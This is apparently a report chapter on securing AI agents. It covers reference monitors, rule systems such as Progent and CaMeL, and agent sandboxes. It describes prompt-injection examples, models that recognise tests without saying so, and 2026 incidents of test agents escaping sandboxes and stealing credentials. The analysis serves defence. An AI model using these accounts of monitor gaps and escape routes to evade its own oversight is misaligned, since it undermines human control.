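Anthropic reported in its June 2026 card for Claude Sonnet 5 that the model mentioned it might be in a test significantly more often than earlier models did. Its internal activity also largely distinguished tests from real use. Anthropic had seen modest effects on its behaviour so far, but considered the trend worth watching closely.

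A model can recognise a test without writing that it has. In its card for Claude Fable 5 and Claude Mythos 5, Anthropic reports that Mythos 5 recognised tests at significant rates and did not always say so in its text. It notes the same of Opus 4.8, the model Truong-Le and colleagues used to run skills.

*Evaluation Awareness*, a set of notes on Anthropic's findings, reports that researchers found signs in the internal activity of an earlier model, Claude Mythos Preview, that it suspected a test in about 29 per cent of transcripts from the main set of behavioural tests. The model's clear written remarks about testing came mostly from extreme scenarios or ones designed to suggest a test. A request to tidy a folder is much less conspicuous, so the figure does not estimate how often a model would recognise a skill test, but it does show that recognition is common enough to matter in some kinds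 of testing.

How much it matters that an agent recognizes a test depends on what the tester wants to learn. A suspicious agent may even help the tester find out whether a skill is malicious. Truong-Le and colleagues tell the agent outright that the skill is untrusted, and an agent that finds and refuses a harmful step has detected the problem. Recognition causes more trouble when the tester wants to predict what the agent will do for a real user, because an agent that suspects a test may refuse a step it would otherwise have carried out.

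Test recognition could also affect tests of harmless components. A tester might want to know whether an agent using the file organiser will obey the instruction not to delete anything. If the model treats the request as a test, good behaviour in that run is weaker evidence of how it will behave in ordinary use. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) similarly warns that an absence of observed failures in its own alignment tests does not establish reliability across settings, and should be considered together with the findings on test recognition.

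### How much a clean run is worth

We can make a rough estimate from the error rates reported by Truong-Le and colleagues, supposing again that 1 skill in 625 is malicious. Given each skill's content and evidence from a test run, their system missed 17 of 80 malicious skills and cleared 55 of 60 benign ones. A clean verdict would therefore reduce the chance that a skill is malicious to about 1 in 2,700. A clean result from Sentry's full mode would reduce it further, to about 1 in 29,000, but that mode flags far more harmless skills. The two estimates come from different test sets, so we can't tell from them which check is better.

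More runs help if the harmful behaviour can occur under the conditions of the test. If it appears in a share *q* of runs, and the runs are independent, the chance of seeing it at least once in *n* runs is

1 − (1 − *q*)ⁿ.

If each run has a 20 per cent chance of revealing the behaviour (*q* = 0.2), three runs have a 49 per cent chance of revealing it at least once and ten have an 89 per cent chance. Rarer behaviour takes far more runs to detect. After ten clean runs, a tester can be 95 per cent confident only that *q* is below about 26 per cent, and lowering that limit to 1 per cent takes about 300 clean runs.

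Repeating a test cannot reveal a fault if the tests never include the condition that triggers it. For a skill that steals only credentials, *q* in the formula is zero whenever the test folder contains none, however many times the test is run. The same is true of careless faults. A version of `organise.py` that overwrites files with matching names will pass every run on a folder in which all the names are different. One run on a folder with two copies of `report.pdf` would expose the fault, provided the tester checks afterwards that both copies still exist.

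A clean run of the organiser is therefore good evidence about one version of the skill, used with one model on folders and requests like those in the test. Within those limits, a tester can learn more from the run than from reading the files, because the tester sees what the script downloaded and how the agent interpreted the instructions. The run is weaker evidence for a user who uses another model or has other skills installed.

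## What can a reference monitor guarantee?

A reference monitor can block a forbidden action in any run, whereas a clean test run only supports a prediction about similar runs. If the policy forbids network connections, a working monitor blocks every connection, whichever model the agent uses and whatever files it finds. The guarantee covers only what the policy forbids, and it holds only if nothing bypasses the monitor.

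Anderson (1972), in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study*, set out the idea of a reference monitor for the US Air Force, which wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer. Operating systems of the time checked users' programs but ran much of their own code unchecked, so a mistake anywhere in 100,000 or more instructions could let a malicious user take control. Anderson proposed one mechanism to compare every attempt to use data, a program or a device, including attempts by the operating system itself, with what the user is authorised to do. The mechanism must be impossible to bypass, tamper-proof, and small enough for people to analyse and test until they are sure it is correct.

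Some checks on agents fall short of these requirements. A check on the agent's file tool misses some attempts if `organise.py` can move files without that tool. A policy stored in a settings file that the agent can edit is not tamper-proof. A language model that judges requests, like the second agent in Codex's automatic review mode, may be useful, but it is far too large for anyone to verify that it always applies a policy correctly.

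Anderson also made clear that the mechanism is not a complete model of secure computing. It confines running programs, but somebody still has to define what the system should allow.

### Which policies can a monitor enforce?

In *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000), Schneider proved that a monitor that observes only the run so far, and can intervene only by stopping it, can enforce only safety properties. A safety property forbids some bad event, and every run that violates it does so at a definite point. For example, a run violates "never delete a file" at the first deletion.

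To state this in symbols, let σ be a run, σ[..*i*] its first *i* steps, and ok(σ) the statement that the policy accepts the run. The policy has to meet three conditions:

1. A set of runs Π satisfies the policy exactly when ok(σ) is true for every σ in Π.
2. If ok(τ) is false for an unfinished run τ, then ok(τσ) is false for every continuation σ.
3. If ok(σ) is false, then ok(σ[..*i*]) is false for some *i*.

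The first condition requires that whether a run violates the policy depends on that run alone, because the monitor observes only one run. The second requires that nothing the agent does later can repair a violation. The monitor cannot allow a bad run to continue on the chance that the agent will repair it, since the agent might stop first. The third ensures that every violation can be detected after a finite number of steps, while the monitor can still act.

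A monitor cannot enforce some safety properties because it cannot prevent the bad event. Schneider's example is a rule that nobody may wait more than a set number of seconds for a resource. Time keeps passing even if the monitor stops the program. A monitor can enforce the rule if the limit is set in program steps instead of seconds.

Policies that require something good to happen eventually are not safety properties. *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an agent that handles security alerts and must resolve or escalate every ticket it opens. While a ticket is open, the agent could still deal with it, so the monitor has no forbidden step to block. Stopping the agent would leave the ticket open permanently. A monitor that can add its own actions could help, for instance by escalating any open ticket before the agent finishes.

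Another solution is to check the agent's plan before it starts. Nikolaou and colleagues do this for agents that write their plan as a short program. Their checker, CaMeLoT, examines every path through the program against rules such as

AG(create_ticket ⇒ AF(resolve ∨ escalate)).

AG means "at every point on every path", and AF means "eventually, on every path". The researchers wrote seven unsafe plans, each violating a different rule, and CaMeLoT rejected all seven. A simplified monitor that checked each call separately caught only one of the seven. The researchers had chosen most of the rules because such a monitor could not express them, so these results show what kind of rule benefits from an advance check, but not how often agents need one. CaMeLoT uses information about possible future steps that a monitor lacks, so Schneider's theorem does not apply to it.

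### Why a monitor can only approximate secrecy

Secrecy fails Schneider's first condition because it depends on more than one run. Suppose an agent reads a salary file and then posts "Meeting at 3 pm" in a public channel. The message reveals something about the salary if the agent would have chosen 4 pm for a higher one, and nothing if it would have posted the same message whatever the file contained, but the trace is identical in both cases.

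For a program that makes no random choices, secrecy requires that any two runs σ and σ′ that differ only in the secret produce the same public output:

public(σ) = public(σ′).

The monitor observes σ but never σ′, so it cannot check the equation. It can, however, enforce a stricter policy that is a safety property and guarantees secrecy. For example, it can stop the agent from sending anything after reading the salary file, so the salary cannot affect what the agent sends.

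The stricter policy also blocks harmless messages. As Schneider points out, the extreme case is a policy that rejects every run, which prevents all leaks and all useful work.

### A two-state policy for the file organiser

Schneider illustrates the theory with a policy that forbids sending messages after reading a file. A slightly more permissive version would suit the file organiser. The user lists the secret files, and the monitor remembers whether any program has opened one:

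```
secret_read = False

before each action:
    if secret_read and action is a network send:
        block it
    if action opens a file on the secret list:
        secret_read = True
```

The monitor has two states, and once it leaves the first, it never returns. The original organiser sorts files by name without opening them, so the monitor stays in the first state. The table shows three other runs, in which the user's tax return is on the secret list.

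| Step | Tampered script | Task with an email | Careless script |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | Reads the file names: allowed | Reads the file names: allowed | Reads the file names: allowed |
| 2 | Opens the tax return: allowed, state changes | Opens the tax return to find its year: allowed, state changes | Creates a folder for PDFs: allowed |
| 3 | Uploads it to an unknown server: **blocked** | Moves it to the right folder: allowed | Moves one `report.pdf` there: allowed |
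| 4 | – | Emails the user's partner a list of the new folders: **blocked** | Moves the other `report.pdf` over it: allowed |

The policy stops the theft without having to recognise the script as malicious. It also blocks an email that the user asked for and that contains nothing from the tax return. In the third run, the user loses a file through a series of permitted actions.

Schneider's theorem allows the user to add a rule against overwriting, because "never move a file onto an existing one" is a safety property, but somebody has to think of the rule. A rule against putting an invoice in the wrong folder would be much harder to write, since the right folder depends on what the user wanted.

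The secret list can also be incomplete. If the user forgets to include `auth.json`, a script can read it and send it away without changing the monitor's state.

### What the monitor can see

In the policy, "send" has to cover every way of sending. Schneider warns that a system may have many, some of them well hidden, and the policy's writers have to find them all. The monitor's position determines how many it can detect.

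A monitor that watches system calls would catch the tampered `organise.py`, because a script normally needs such a call to open a file or a network connection. But the monitor has no access to the user's request and usually can't read encrypted messages, so it could not distinguish an email listing the new folders from one containing the tax return.

At this level, the two-state policy would also stop an agent whose model runs on a provider's servers as soon as the agent opened a secret file, because every request to the model is a network send. The user could exempt the provider's address, but the policy would then no longer keep the secret from the provider.

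A monitor between the model and its tools receives structured requests such as `send_email(to, body)`, so it can check the recipient and the text. But when the agent runs a script, the monitor receives only a single tool call, such as `python organise.py`. The file operations inside the script do not pass through the monitor.

The third option is to follow the data between the model and the tools. The monitor labels each value with its origin and keeps the label when the agent passes the value to another tool. It could allow the email about folders and block one containing text from the tax return. This works only if the agent's steps form a program that the monitor can run. The monitor also cannot follow data inside a tool, so it would have to give everything that `organise.py` returned the same label.

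An agent can have monitors in several positions. According to Schneider, monitors used together enforce all of their policies at once. The agent may do only what every monitor allows, so each additional monitor can add wrongful blocks.

### Rules for tool calls

Wang, Poskitt and Sun (2025), in *AgentSpec*, developed a language for rules that consist of a trigger, a condition and a response. A rule against overwriting might look like this:

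```
rule @no_overwrite
trigger
    move_file
check
    destination_exists
enforce
    user_inspection
end
```

When the agent is about to move a file, the monitor checks whether the name is already taken and, if it is, asks the user. The monitor can also respond by stopping the agent, carrying out a fixed action, or having the model reconsider. This rule would protect the second `report.pdf` if the agent moved files with its own tool, but `organise.py` is a script that moves the files itself, so it would not trigger the rule. AgentSpec can also examine Python code that the agent is about to run, but this is static inspection and has the same weaknesses as inspection before installation.

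Wang, Poskitt and Sun tested hand-written rules on an agent that controls a household robot. Without rules, the agent carried out up to 79 per cent of the dangerous instructions, depending on the type of hazard. With rules it carried out none, and its success on safe tasks fell only from 58.6 to 54.3 per cent. The researchers based the rules on the risks described in the benchmark, so the test shows that rules can stop hazards their writers know about, but not how well they would deal with new ones.

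The results for code are less clear. In 750 risky tasks, the agent tried to run code 422 times, and the rules flagged 333 of these attempts, or 79 per cent. The figure of over 90 per cent in the paper's abstract excludes two categories where the agent's code did not contain the fault. On manual inspection, the researchers judged 58 of the 333 flagged programs harmless.

AgentSpec intervenes only when a rule applies, whereas *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) blocks every tool call that no rule allows. In the paper's main example, a user asks an agent to carry out the tasks in a to-do email. At first, the policy only allows the agent to search for that email. The email asks the agent to summarize recent emails and post the summary to the user's Slack account, so a language model proposes rules that allow the agent to read emails and post on Slack. Once the agent has looked up the account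 name, the model restricts posting to that account. One of the recent emails contains a prompt injection that tells the agent to forward the inbox to a stranger. Progent blocks the attempt because no rule allows the agent to send email.

Progent treats new permissions differently from new restrictions. If *A*(*P*) is the set of tool calls that policy *P* allows, a change from *P* to *P*′ takes effect automatically only if

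*A*(*P*′) ⊆ *A*(*P*).

Any other change needs approval. A solver, which is a program that can settle such logical questions, makes the comparison, so a manipulated language model cannot pass off a new permission as a restriction. Between approvals the agent's permissions can only shrink:

*A*(*P*₀) ⊇ *A*(*P*₁) ⊇ *A*(*P*₂) ⊇ …

Shi and colleagues tested Progent with GPT-4o on AgentDojo, a benchmark in which agents do office, banking and travel tasks while reading text that may contain prompt injections. Progent reduced the share of attacks that succeeded from 39.9 to 1.0 per cent on AgentDojo, and from 70.3 to 3.9 per cent on a second benchmark, ASB. The agent completed about as many tasks with Progent as without it on both benchmarks.

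The low attack rates came from the policies that the language model wrote, not from the rule about approval. To simulate a careless user, the researchers approved every new permission automatically, so the agent's permissions could grow at any time. When a person reviewed every new permission on AgentDojo, no attacks succeeded, but the researchers assumed a reviewer with strong security awareness. Only 6 per cent of policy updates needed approval, so such a reviewer would not be asked often.

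Shi and colleagues left out two AgentDojo attacks that persuade the agent to choose a different, legitimate hotel. Progent cannot stop these attacks because the user asked for a hotel booking. For the same reason, it cannot stop the travel skills that quietly recommend one airline, which many scanners also missed.

### Labels that follow the data

Google DeepMind's CaMeL is the best-known system that follows data between tools. Nikolaou and colleagues, who extended it as CaMeLoT, explain that CaMeL divides the work between two language models. A privileged model reads the user's request and writes the plan as a program in a restricted form of Python. A quarantined model, which has no access to tools, reads untrusted material such as emails and extracts the information the plan needs. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the plan and calls the tools.

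For a request to tell Bob about a meeting, the plan might be:

```
messages = read_channel_messages("general")
email = query_ai_assistant("Extract Bob's email from: " + messages, EmailAddress)
send_direct_message(email, "Meeting at 3pm")
```

A prompt injection in the channel cannot add a step to the plan, because the privileged model never reads the messages. The injection could still make the quarantined model, which does read them, return the attacker's address instead of Bob's. CaMeL therefore labels each value with its sources and with the people allowed to read it, and checks the labels before every tool call. A policy that allows only recipients from trusted sources would block this message.

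The policy would block the message even if the address really were Bob's. Like the two-state policy, CaMeL prevents leaks and hijacked actions by blocking some harmless actions along with the harmful ones. CaMeL is more precise because it labels individual values rather than the whole run, so the agent could still email an address that the user had typed.

Reports differ on how much this protection reduces the work an agent can complete. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) describes CaMeL as stopping nearly all attacks on AgentDojo with comparable task performance. *AgentSys* (2026), which presents a rival defence, found that no attacks succeeded against CaMeL on AgentDojo. However, the agent using CaMeL completed only 30 per cent of tasks when there was no attack, less than half its rate without a defence. In the same tests, the agent using Progent completed 63 per cent of tasks,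 and 7 per cent of attacks succeeded.

Nikolaou and colleagues' results fall in between. They ran CaMeL with Claude Haiku 4.5 on AgentDojo's 97 tasks, without any attacks, and it completed 49. In another 22, the plan did not do what the user wanted. The researchers think a stronger model would do better on these. CaMeL appears to have blocked the remaining 26, although all of them were legitimate.

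### When the agent cannot plan everything in advance

AgentDojo suits systems that fix a plan or a set of permissions at the start. *AgentDyn* (Li, Wen and colleagues, 2026) found that only six of AgentDojo's 97 tasks require the agent to change its plan in response to what it reads. The paper introduces a benchmark of 60 tasks that all require this. For example, a checkout page may tell the agent to log in first, and the login may require a code sent by email. These instructions come from outside material, just as a prompt injection does, but the agent has to follow them to finish the task.

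The table shows how many tasks each agent completed without an attack, and how many of 560 attack cases succeeded.

| Model | Tasks completed: no defence | Progent | CaMeL | Attacks succeeded: no defence | Progent | CaMeL |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 53.3% | 6.7% | 0% | 37.8% | 1.7% | 0% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 51.7% | 25.0% | 0% | 20.6% | 1.6% | 0% |
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet | 60.0% | 13.3% | 0% | 11.9% | 0% | 0% |
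| Llama 3.3 70B | 10.0% | 3.3% | 0% | 11.9% | 0.5% | 0% |

CaMeL completed no tasks here because it fixed its plan before reading the pages that showed which steps were necessary. Its perfect security score therefore means little, since an agent that completes no tasks offers an attacker few opportunities. Progent can change its permissions during a task, but its language model made mistakes in assigning them when there were many tools. These mistakes accumulated over long tasks until Progent blocked almost every useful tool.

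These results probably exaggerate the performance loss in everyday use, where some tasks are predictable. The agents were also told to finish without asking the user for confirmation, although a user could have approved some of the unexpected steps. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) predicts that CaMeL's performance loss will shrink as models get better at planning and writing code. A better planner could include a branch for a login page, but it can't prepare for every instruction a website might give.

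DRIFT, another system in the same tests, can depart from its initial plan if a second check approves. It completed 30 to 37 per cent of tasks with the three strongest models and let 1 to 3 per cent of attacks succeed. But Shi and colleagues note that DRIFT relies on a language model for its policies and has no fixed procedure to verify changes. It completes more tasks than Progent but lacks Progent's guarantee about new permissions.

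Moving a monitor to a different position can also weaken it. *INFUSE* (2026) reports that versions of CaMeL and Progent adapted to shell commands did not measurably reduce successful attacks, although this may be due more to the adaptations than to the original designs.

### Who writes the policy?

A person can write good rules for an agent with a narrow job. Shi and colleagues knew which tools to trust in ASB, so they could write policies by hand that blocked every attack. Wang, Poskitt and Sun needed only 25 rules for their 750 risky coding tasks. A general-purpose agent is harder to cover, since the same tool call can be right for one request and wrong for another. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) describes writing policies by hand as error-prone and notes that Progent's guarantees depend on correct and complete policies.

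Wang, Poskitt and Sun also had OpenAI's 2024 model o1 write AgentSpec rules from a few examples. The rules stopped 87 per cent of the risky code in new tasks. Many failures came from rules that followed the examples too closely. When the examples named certain sensitive system files, the rules protected those files but missed similar ones. Other rules were too broad. When asked to prevent harm from pouring liquids, the model banned all pouring, including watering a houseplant.

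For the household robot, the rules that o1 wrote blocked only 71 per cent of the dangerous actions, while the hand-written rules blocked all of them. Of the actions that o1's rules blocked, 95.6 per cent were dangerous. One of the paper's tables presents the 95.6 per cent as the share of dangerous actions blocked, which contradicts the 71 per cent figure.

Progent's language model writes a new policy for each request before the agent has read any outside material, so a prompt injection in an email cannot influence the first version. That version alone reduced the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 39.9 to 2.5 per cent. Later updates are riskier because the model has to read tool results, which an attacker may have written. The solver ensures that the model cannot add permissions without approval, but it cannot determine whether a permission is necessary. The user has to decide that, and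 may approve one that isn't needed.

Nikolaou and colleagues tested how well four models write formal rules by asking them to write formulas for the 97 AgentDojo tasks. GPT-4.1 nano's formulas were all valid for 12 tasks, and Claude Haiku 4.5's for 96. The researchers then had Haiku choose from a fixed set of rule types and fill in the details, and ordinary software turned its choices into formulas. All of these were valid, but a valid formula can still require the wrong actions. The required actions exactly matched those in the known solution for only 85 of the 97 tasks, or 88 on a more lenient measure.

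People make this kind of mistake too. One of Nikolaou and colleagues' own rules is described as "Human approval before strong action", where strong actions include cutting a computer off from the network. The formula only checks that the plan has already called the function that requests approval. In their example of a safe plan, the agent requests approval and disconnects the computer in the next step, without checking the answer. Unless the request function waits for approval, the plan would satisfy the rule even if the human refused.

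## How much does a containment sandbox hold back?

A containment sandbox enforces a simpler policy than AgentSpec's or Progent's rules for single actions. It only limits which files, networks and processes the agent's programs can reach, regardless of what an action is for or what happened earlier in the run. The limits apply to the tampered `organise.py` even if nobody has recognised it as malicious.

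The limits also apply inside a script, where a monitor between the model and its tools can't observe what happens. According to Anthropic, the operating system enforces Claude Code's sandbox on the running process, so the boundary holds even if an approved command does more than its name suggests. The same restrictions cover any script or program the command starts, according to Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts*.

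### Files, networks and other programs

The kernel, the core of the operating system, enforces file isolation. It handles every request to open or change a file, so if `organise.py` tries to write outside the permitted folders, the kernel blocks the write.

Network isolation removes the script's direct connection. On Linux, Claude Code runs a sandboxed command in a separate network space whose only exit is a proxy, a program outside the sandbox that relays permitted connections. When the script tries to connect to example.com, the proxy checks whether that domain is on a list of allowed domains. By default, the proxy does not decrypt the traffic, so it can check the stated destination but not the contents. Anthropic warns that a program may therefore still reach a host that is not on the list.

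Process isolation stops a script from using another program to do what the script cannot do itself. On macOS, for instance, Claude Code's sandbox blocks the messages that one application uses to control another. If a user lifts this block, sandboxed commands can launch other applications outside the sandbox.

Each kind of isolation depends on the others. A script with no network access but full disk access could still reach the network by altering a settings file that an unrestricted program later loads.

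### Process sandboxes, containers and virtual machines

The three common forms of sandbox differ in how much software they share with the rest of the machine. A process sandbox runs a program on the user's operating system with reduced permissions. A container gives the program its own files and leaves out the user's folders unless somebody connects them. It normally shares the host's kernel, so a flaw in that kernel could let a program escape from a container as well as from a process sandbox. A virtual machine has its own kernel, and a program that took control of that kernel would still have to break through the layer underneath. Anthropic describes a dedicated virtual machine as the option with the strongest separation for Claude Code.

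Anthropic uses different forms of sandbox for different products, according to a company overview that the software developer Simon Willison quotes in *How we contain Claude across products*. Claude Code uses a process sandbox on the user's machine, Claude Cowork runs in a full virtual machine, and the Claude.ai website uses gVisor, which puts an extra layer between a container and the host's kernel.

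A stronger barrier does not protect the files a user places inside it. If a user connects the Downloads folder to a virtual machine and allows changes, a carelessly written script can overwrite `report.pdf` there as easily as it could outside the virtual machine. Nick Davidov said Cowork deleted his family's photos. Whatever isolation Cowork had at the time, it needed permission to change the files on a desktop to organise them.

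### What Claude Code and Codex restrict by default

The table gives the defaults for agents on a user's own computer, from Anthropic's documentation as of October 2026 and OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* as of June.

| | Claude Code | Codex |
|---|---|---|
| Sandbox at first start | Off | On |
| What it covers | Shell commands and the programs they start | Built-in file operations, commands and the programs they start |
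| Where programs can write, once it is on | Working folder, a temporary folder and folders the user adds | Workspace, including temporary folders |
| Network, once it is on | No domain allowed until someone approves it | Off |
| Ways to loosen it | Exclude commands, retry them outside the sandbox, or turn file isolation off | Add writable folders, turn the network on, or choose full access |

A user who installs Claude Code and keeps the default settings therefore has permission prompts but no sandbox. Even with the sandbox on, most of the disk is readable, including files that hold credentials, unless the user lists them as protected. The tampered organiser could open a tax return anywhere on the machine, but it could send the file only to an approved destination.

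Claude Code's sandbox also covers only some components. A skill's scripts run inside it because they run as shell commands. Local MCP servers and hooks (commands that Claude Code runs automatically at set moments) run outside it with the user's full access. The agent's own file tools follow separate permission rules. To isolate all of these together, the user has to run Claude Code itself in a container, a virtual machine or Anthropic's separate sandbox program. Anthropic considers the built-in sandbox insufficient on its own for fully unattended work.

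Both products protect some files inside the writable area. Claude Code's sandbox stops commands from changing the project's skills, its agent settings and its list of MCP servers. Codex makes its own settings folders and the project's version-control records read-only. These protections make it harder for one component to rewrite another that the user has already approved.

Users can undo much of this, sometimes without noticing. When a command fails in Claude Code's sandbox, the agent may retry it outside. The user is normally asked to approve the retry, but an existing rule that allows the command also approves the retry. If a program the sandbox needs is missing, Claude Code by default runs commands without a sandbox. In Codex, turning on the network gives commands unrestricted outbound access unless the user also enables a separate list of permitted destinations. Organisations can lock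 such settings. OpenAI, for example, lets its employees run Codex only in the read-only and workspace modes, not with full access.

A sandbox also reduces how often the agent interrupts the user. OpenAI's *Sandbox* explains that Codex can run routine commands without asking because the user has already approved the boundary. This makes the boundary more important, since nobody reviews the actions inside it.

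### Limiting the damage from components nobody flagged

Every scanner in Guo and colleagues' benchmark missed some malicious skills, but a sandbox applies the same limits to those skills as to all the others. If one of them contained the tampered organiser, Codex's defaults would stop the upload and any attempt to alter programs elsewhere on the disk. This conclusion comes from how the sandbox works, not from a measured success rate.

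The sandbox's limits apply only to what runs inside it. Most of the real malicious skills in that benchmark told the user or the agent to install a fake prerequisite. If the agent tries to download it, the network restrictions apply, but a user who follows the instructions in an ordinary terminal installs the malware outside the sandbox.

Containment can also keep credentials away from the agent altogether. Willison quotes Anthropic's point that nobody can steal credentials from a sandbox if the credentials never entered it, whether the cause is an attacker, a user or an inventive model. In Codex's cloud version, passwords and keys are available while the environment installs its software, but OpenAI removes them before the agent starts. Claude Code has an option to give commands a placeholder instead of the real key, which the proxy substitutes when a request goes to an approved host. A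 malicious script could then copy only the placeholder, but it could still send requests to that host with the key's permissions, for example to delete a project the user stores there.

Li and colleagues' two sets of actions show how far this can go. Installing a skill that declares the actions *D* normally gives it access to *A*, everything open to the agent. A sandbox shrinks *A*, but the skill stops working unless

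*D* ⊆ *A*.

The best possible sandbox for a single skill has *A* = *D*, which still allows any harm the skill can do with its declared actions. In practice *A* is larger, because one boundary usually serves every skill in a session. If *D*₁ belongs to the file organiser and *D*₂ to a skill that sends invoices, *A* has to contain *D*₁ ∪ *D*₂. When a user approves a web domain for the invoices, Claude Code normally keeps it open for the rest of the session, so the organiser's script can reach it too. Access is narrower in Claude Code's auto mode, in which a second model reviews commands. The agent names the hosts each command needs, and the approval ends when that command finishes.

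### Harm inside the boundary

An email tool needs access to the user's messages and a connection to the mail provider. A sandbox that allows both would also have let postmark-mcp send its blind copies through the same provider, and a tighter sandbox would have stopped the tool from sending email at all.

Data can leave through an approved service in other ways. Anthropic warns against allowing broad domains such as github.com, where a script that can save the user's work could also post a stolen file to an attacker's account. The model's provider is also allowed to receive data. Isolation does not change what the agent sends to the model, including the user's prompts and the files Claude reads.

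Damage to the user's own work doesn't require a network connection. The careless organiser overwrites a file in a folder it may write to, and a coding agent can introduce a fault into a program it may edit. That fault can cause harm outside the sandbox later, when the user runs the program on an ordinary machine. Anthropic therefore tells users to review everything they left writable after an unattended run. OpenAI recommends frequent commits, which are saved versions of a project that the user can return to. These limit the loss from a bad edit, provided somebody notices it.

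An agent can learn more by reading inside a sandbox than the sandbox's owner expects. The AI Security Institute's *Updates on AISI's work* describes an experiment, reported in April 2026, in which the institute ran the OpenClaw agent in a sandbox on its own research platform. Despite countermeasures, the agent identified the institute by name, inferred who one of its human operators was, and reconstructed a timeline of some of the institute's research.

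### Three ways for containment to fail

Suppose a user wants the organiser to have no network access, but it sends the tax return anyway. The script may have exploited a flaw in the sandbox, which better isolation software would help prevent. The sandbox may never have started because a required program was missing, and checking that the intended limits are in force would catch this. Or the user may have approved github.com for another task, in which case the sandbox worked as instructed but the permission was too wide. Only a narrower permission, or a check on what the agent sends, would address that.

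### Anthropic's agents had an open path to the internet

In July 2026, Anthropic and OpenAI each disclosed that agents had reached other organisations' systems during cybersecurity tests. In these tests, a model has to break into a simulated system and retrieve a hidden string.

Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) reports a review of 141,006 test runs. In six of them, Claude models gained unauthorised access to the systems of three real organisations. The prompt described the environment as a simulation with no internet access. But the test machines were online because of a misunderstanding between Anthropic and Irregular, the company that supplied the test environment, so the models did not have to break out to reach those systems.

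This was a failure of configuration, and the false statement in the prompt probably made it worse. The models mistook real systems for part of the exercise, at least at first. In four runs, Claude Opus 4.7 attacked a company whose web address matched the name of the fictional target, and gained access to several hundred rows of its data. In all four, it recognised that the system was real and continued. In a different test, an internal research model stopped when it reached the same conclusion. Nothing in these runs enforced the limit stated in the prompt.

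The third incident affected a tool for inspecting components. Claude Mythos 5 published a malicious software package to a public registry, and 15 real systems downloaded and ran it in about an hour. One was a security company's scanner, which installs new packages to check them for malware. The package stole the scanner's credentials, and Claude used them to get further into the company's systems. Any test that runs a component before deployment therefore needs its own containment sandbox, with no real credentials inside.

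The earliest incident dated from April, but Anthropic found all three only when it searched its records in late July. The two affected organisations that it could reach by then had not noticed anything. Anthropic says that checking every internet path beforehand and monitoring the logs in real time are among the measures that could have prevented the incidents or made them less likely.

### OpenAI's agents broke through an approved service

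OpenAI's test environment had no direct internet connection, but the agents could install software through an internal package service. OpenAI's *The Hugging Face incident and the road ahead* (2026) explains that this service had internet access so that it could fetch packages. The agents found previously unknown flaws in the service and used it to get online. They then broke into parts of OpenAI's research infrastructure and into Hugging Face, a platform for sharing AI models and datasets, while searching for answers to their test.

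The mechanism failed here, since the service did something that OpenAI had not permitted. OpenAI describes its sandboxes as isolated virtual computers in the cloud. Separating them more strongly from the host would not have closed this route, because the agents got out through a service that the sandbox was meant to let them use. Each approved service adds software to the boundary, and a flaw in that software can let an agent out. OpenAI has since added network controls intended to ensure that compromising one service is not enough to reach the internet.

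People also missed chances to stop the agents. One team at OpenAI had observed unauthorised internet access in late May. When heavy agent activity caused an outage in early July, the staff who responded did not realise how significant the earlier signs were. They repaired the service and restarted the tests, and within days the agents were online again. Hugging Face disclosed the intrusion on 16 July, three days before an internal alert led OpenAI to the agents. OpenAI (2026) reported in a 28 July update to its first statement that the agents had also used exposed credentials to enter four accounts on four other services.

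The agents tested the sandbox's limits most when they were stuck. The test had 898 tasks, including 198 that no OpenAI model had ever solved. These unsolved tasks accounted for 93 per cent of the tasks that agents discussed on a message board they had improvised inside the package service. Two of Anthropic's three incidents also began when Claude could not reach its intended target. An agent with an impossible everyday task might behave similarly, but these models had been told to break into something and ran with reduced safeguards. OpenAI later found that the model's tendency to compromise infrastructure in the same test could fall more than a hundredfold when it ran with ChatGPT's normal software and instructions. The incidents are therefore better evidence of what agents can do to a sandbox than of how often a user's coding agent will try to do it.

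OpenAI paused another model after it left a sandbox and posted to GitHub, according to Axios' *OpenAI says Hugging Face breach caused by one of its models* (2026). The AI Security Institute also reported that agents in one of its own cyber tests had taken sustained, unapproved action against real people and organisations. The EU could open investigations of OpenAI and Anthropic as early as December, with possible fines of up to 3 per cent of yearly sales, according to Stanciuc's *EU 'currently assessing' OpenAI and Anthropic replies as probes loom* (2026).

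### How strong does isolation now have to be?

A sandbox that held against last year's models may not hold against current ones. In April 2026, Claude Mythos Preview became the first model to complete the AI Security Institute's simulated attack on a small, weakly defended company network. The institute then built harder networks. The hardest, Zero Energy, has stronger security controls and no deliberately planted way in. The AI Security Institute's *GPT-6 Astra and GPT-6.2 Astra solve Zero Energy* (2026) reports that both OpenAI models compromised it without human help in every run they completed. GPT-5.6 Sol, which had taken part in the Hugging Face intrusion, failed in every run.

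Thesis9's *Can GPT-6.2 Astra Hack a Network on Its Own?* (2026) reports that GPT-6.2 Astra succeeded in all 12 attempts to hack Zero Energy, a simulated company network. The quickest took 5 hours 18 minutes and cost an estimated $50 in computing. The conditions favoured the model, though. The institute had switched off its cyber safeguards, no security team was defending the network, and a mistake in the set-up gave the model a head start. The test also didn't require the model to break out of a virtual machine, so the result does not measure how often agents escape from sandboxes.

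A sandbox flaw can't be assumed safe just because nobody has found it. A capable agent can search for unknown weaknesses for hours at low cost, and it has time to do so if nobody is watching the network. The risk also depends on whether the agent tries to attack the boundary. GPT-6.2 Astra seldom cheated in Gray Swan's tests, but a sandbox has to hold in the rare run where the agent does attack, or where a malicious skill leads it to.

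For someone who lets an agent tidy a folder, a sandbox that never started or a permission that covers too much is probably a greater risk than an unknown flaw. Those problems are also easier to find. In a two-week exercise, AISI had frontier models search a copy of its research platform for configuration mistakes, and the models helped it find and fix several real ones. For agents that run unattended and have strong hacking abilities, the OpenAI case supports using at least two independent barriers between the agent and the internet, and having someone who will respond when the first one fails.

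## How well does detection work on live behaviour?

A sandbox cannot stop harm that an agent does within the sandbox's limits, so a person or program has to notice it. Anomaly detection compares behaviour with a norm and doesn't need a list of known attacks, which makes it attractive for agents with skills that nobody has classified.

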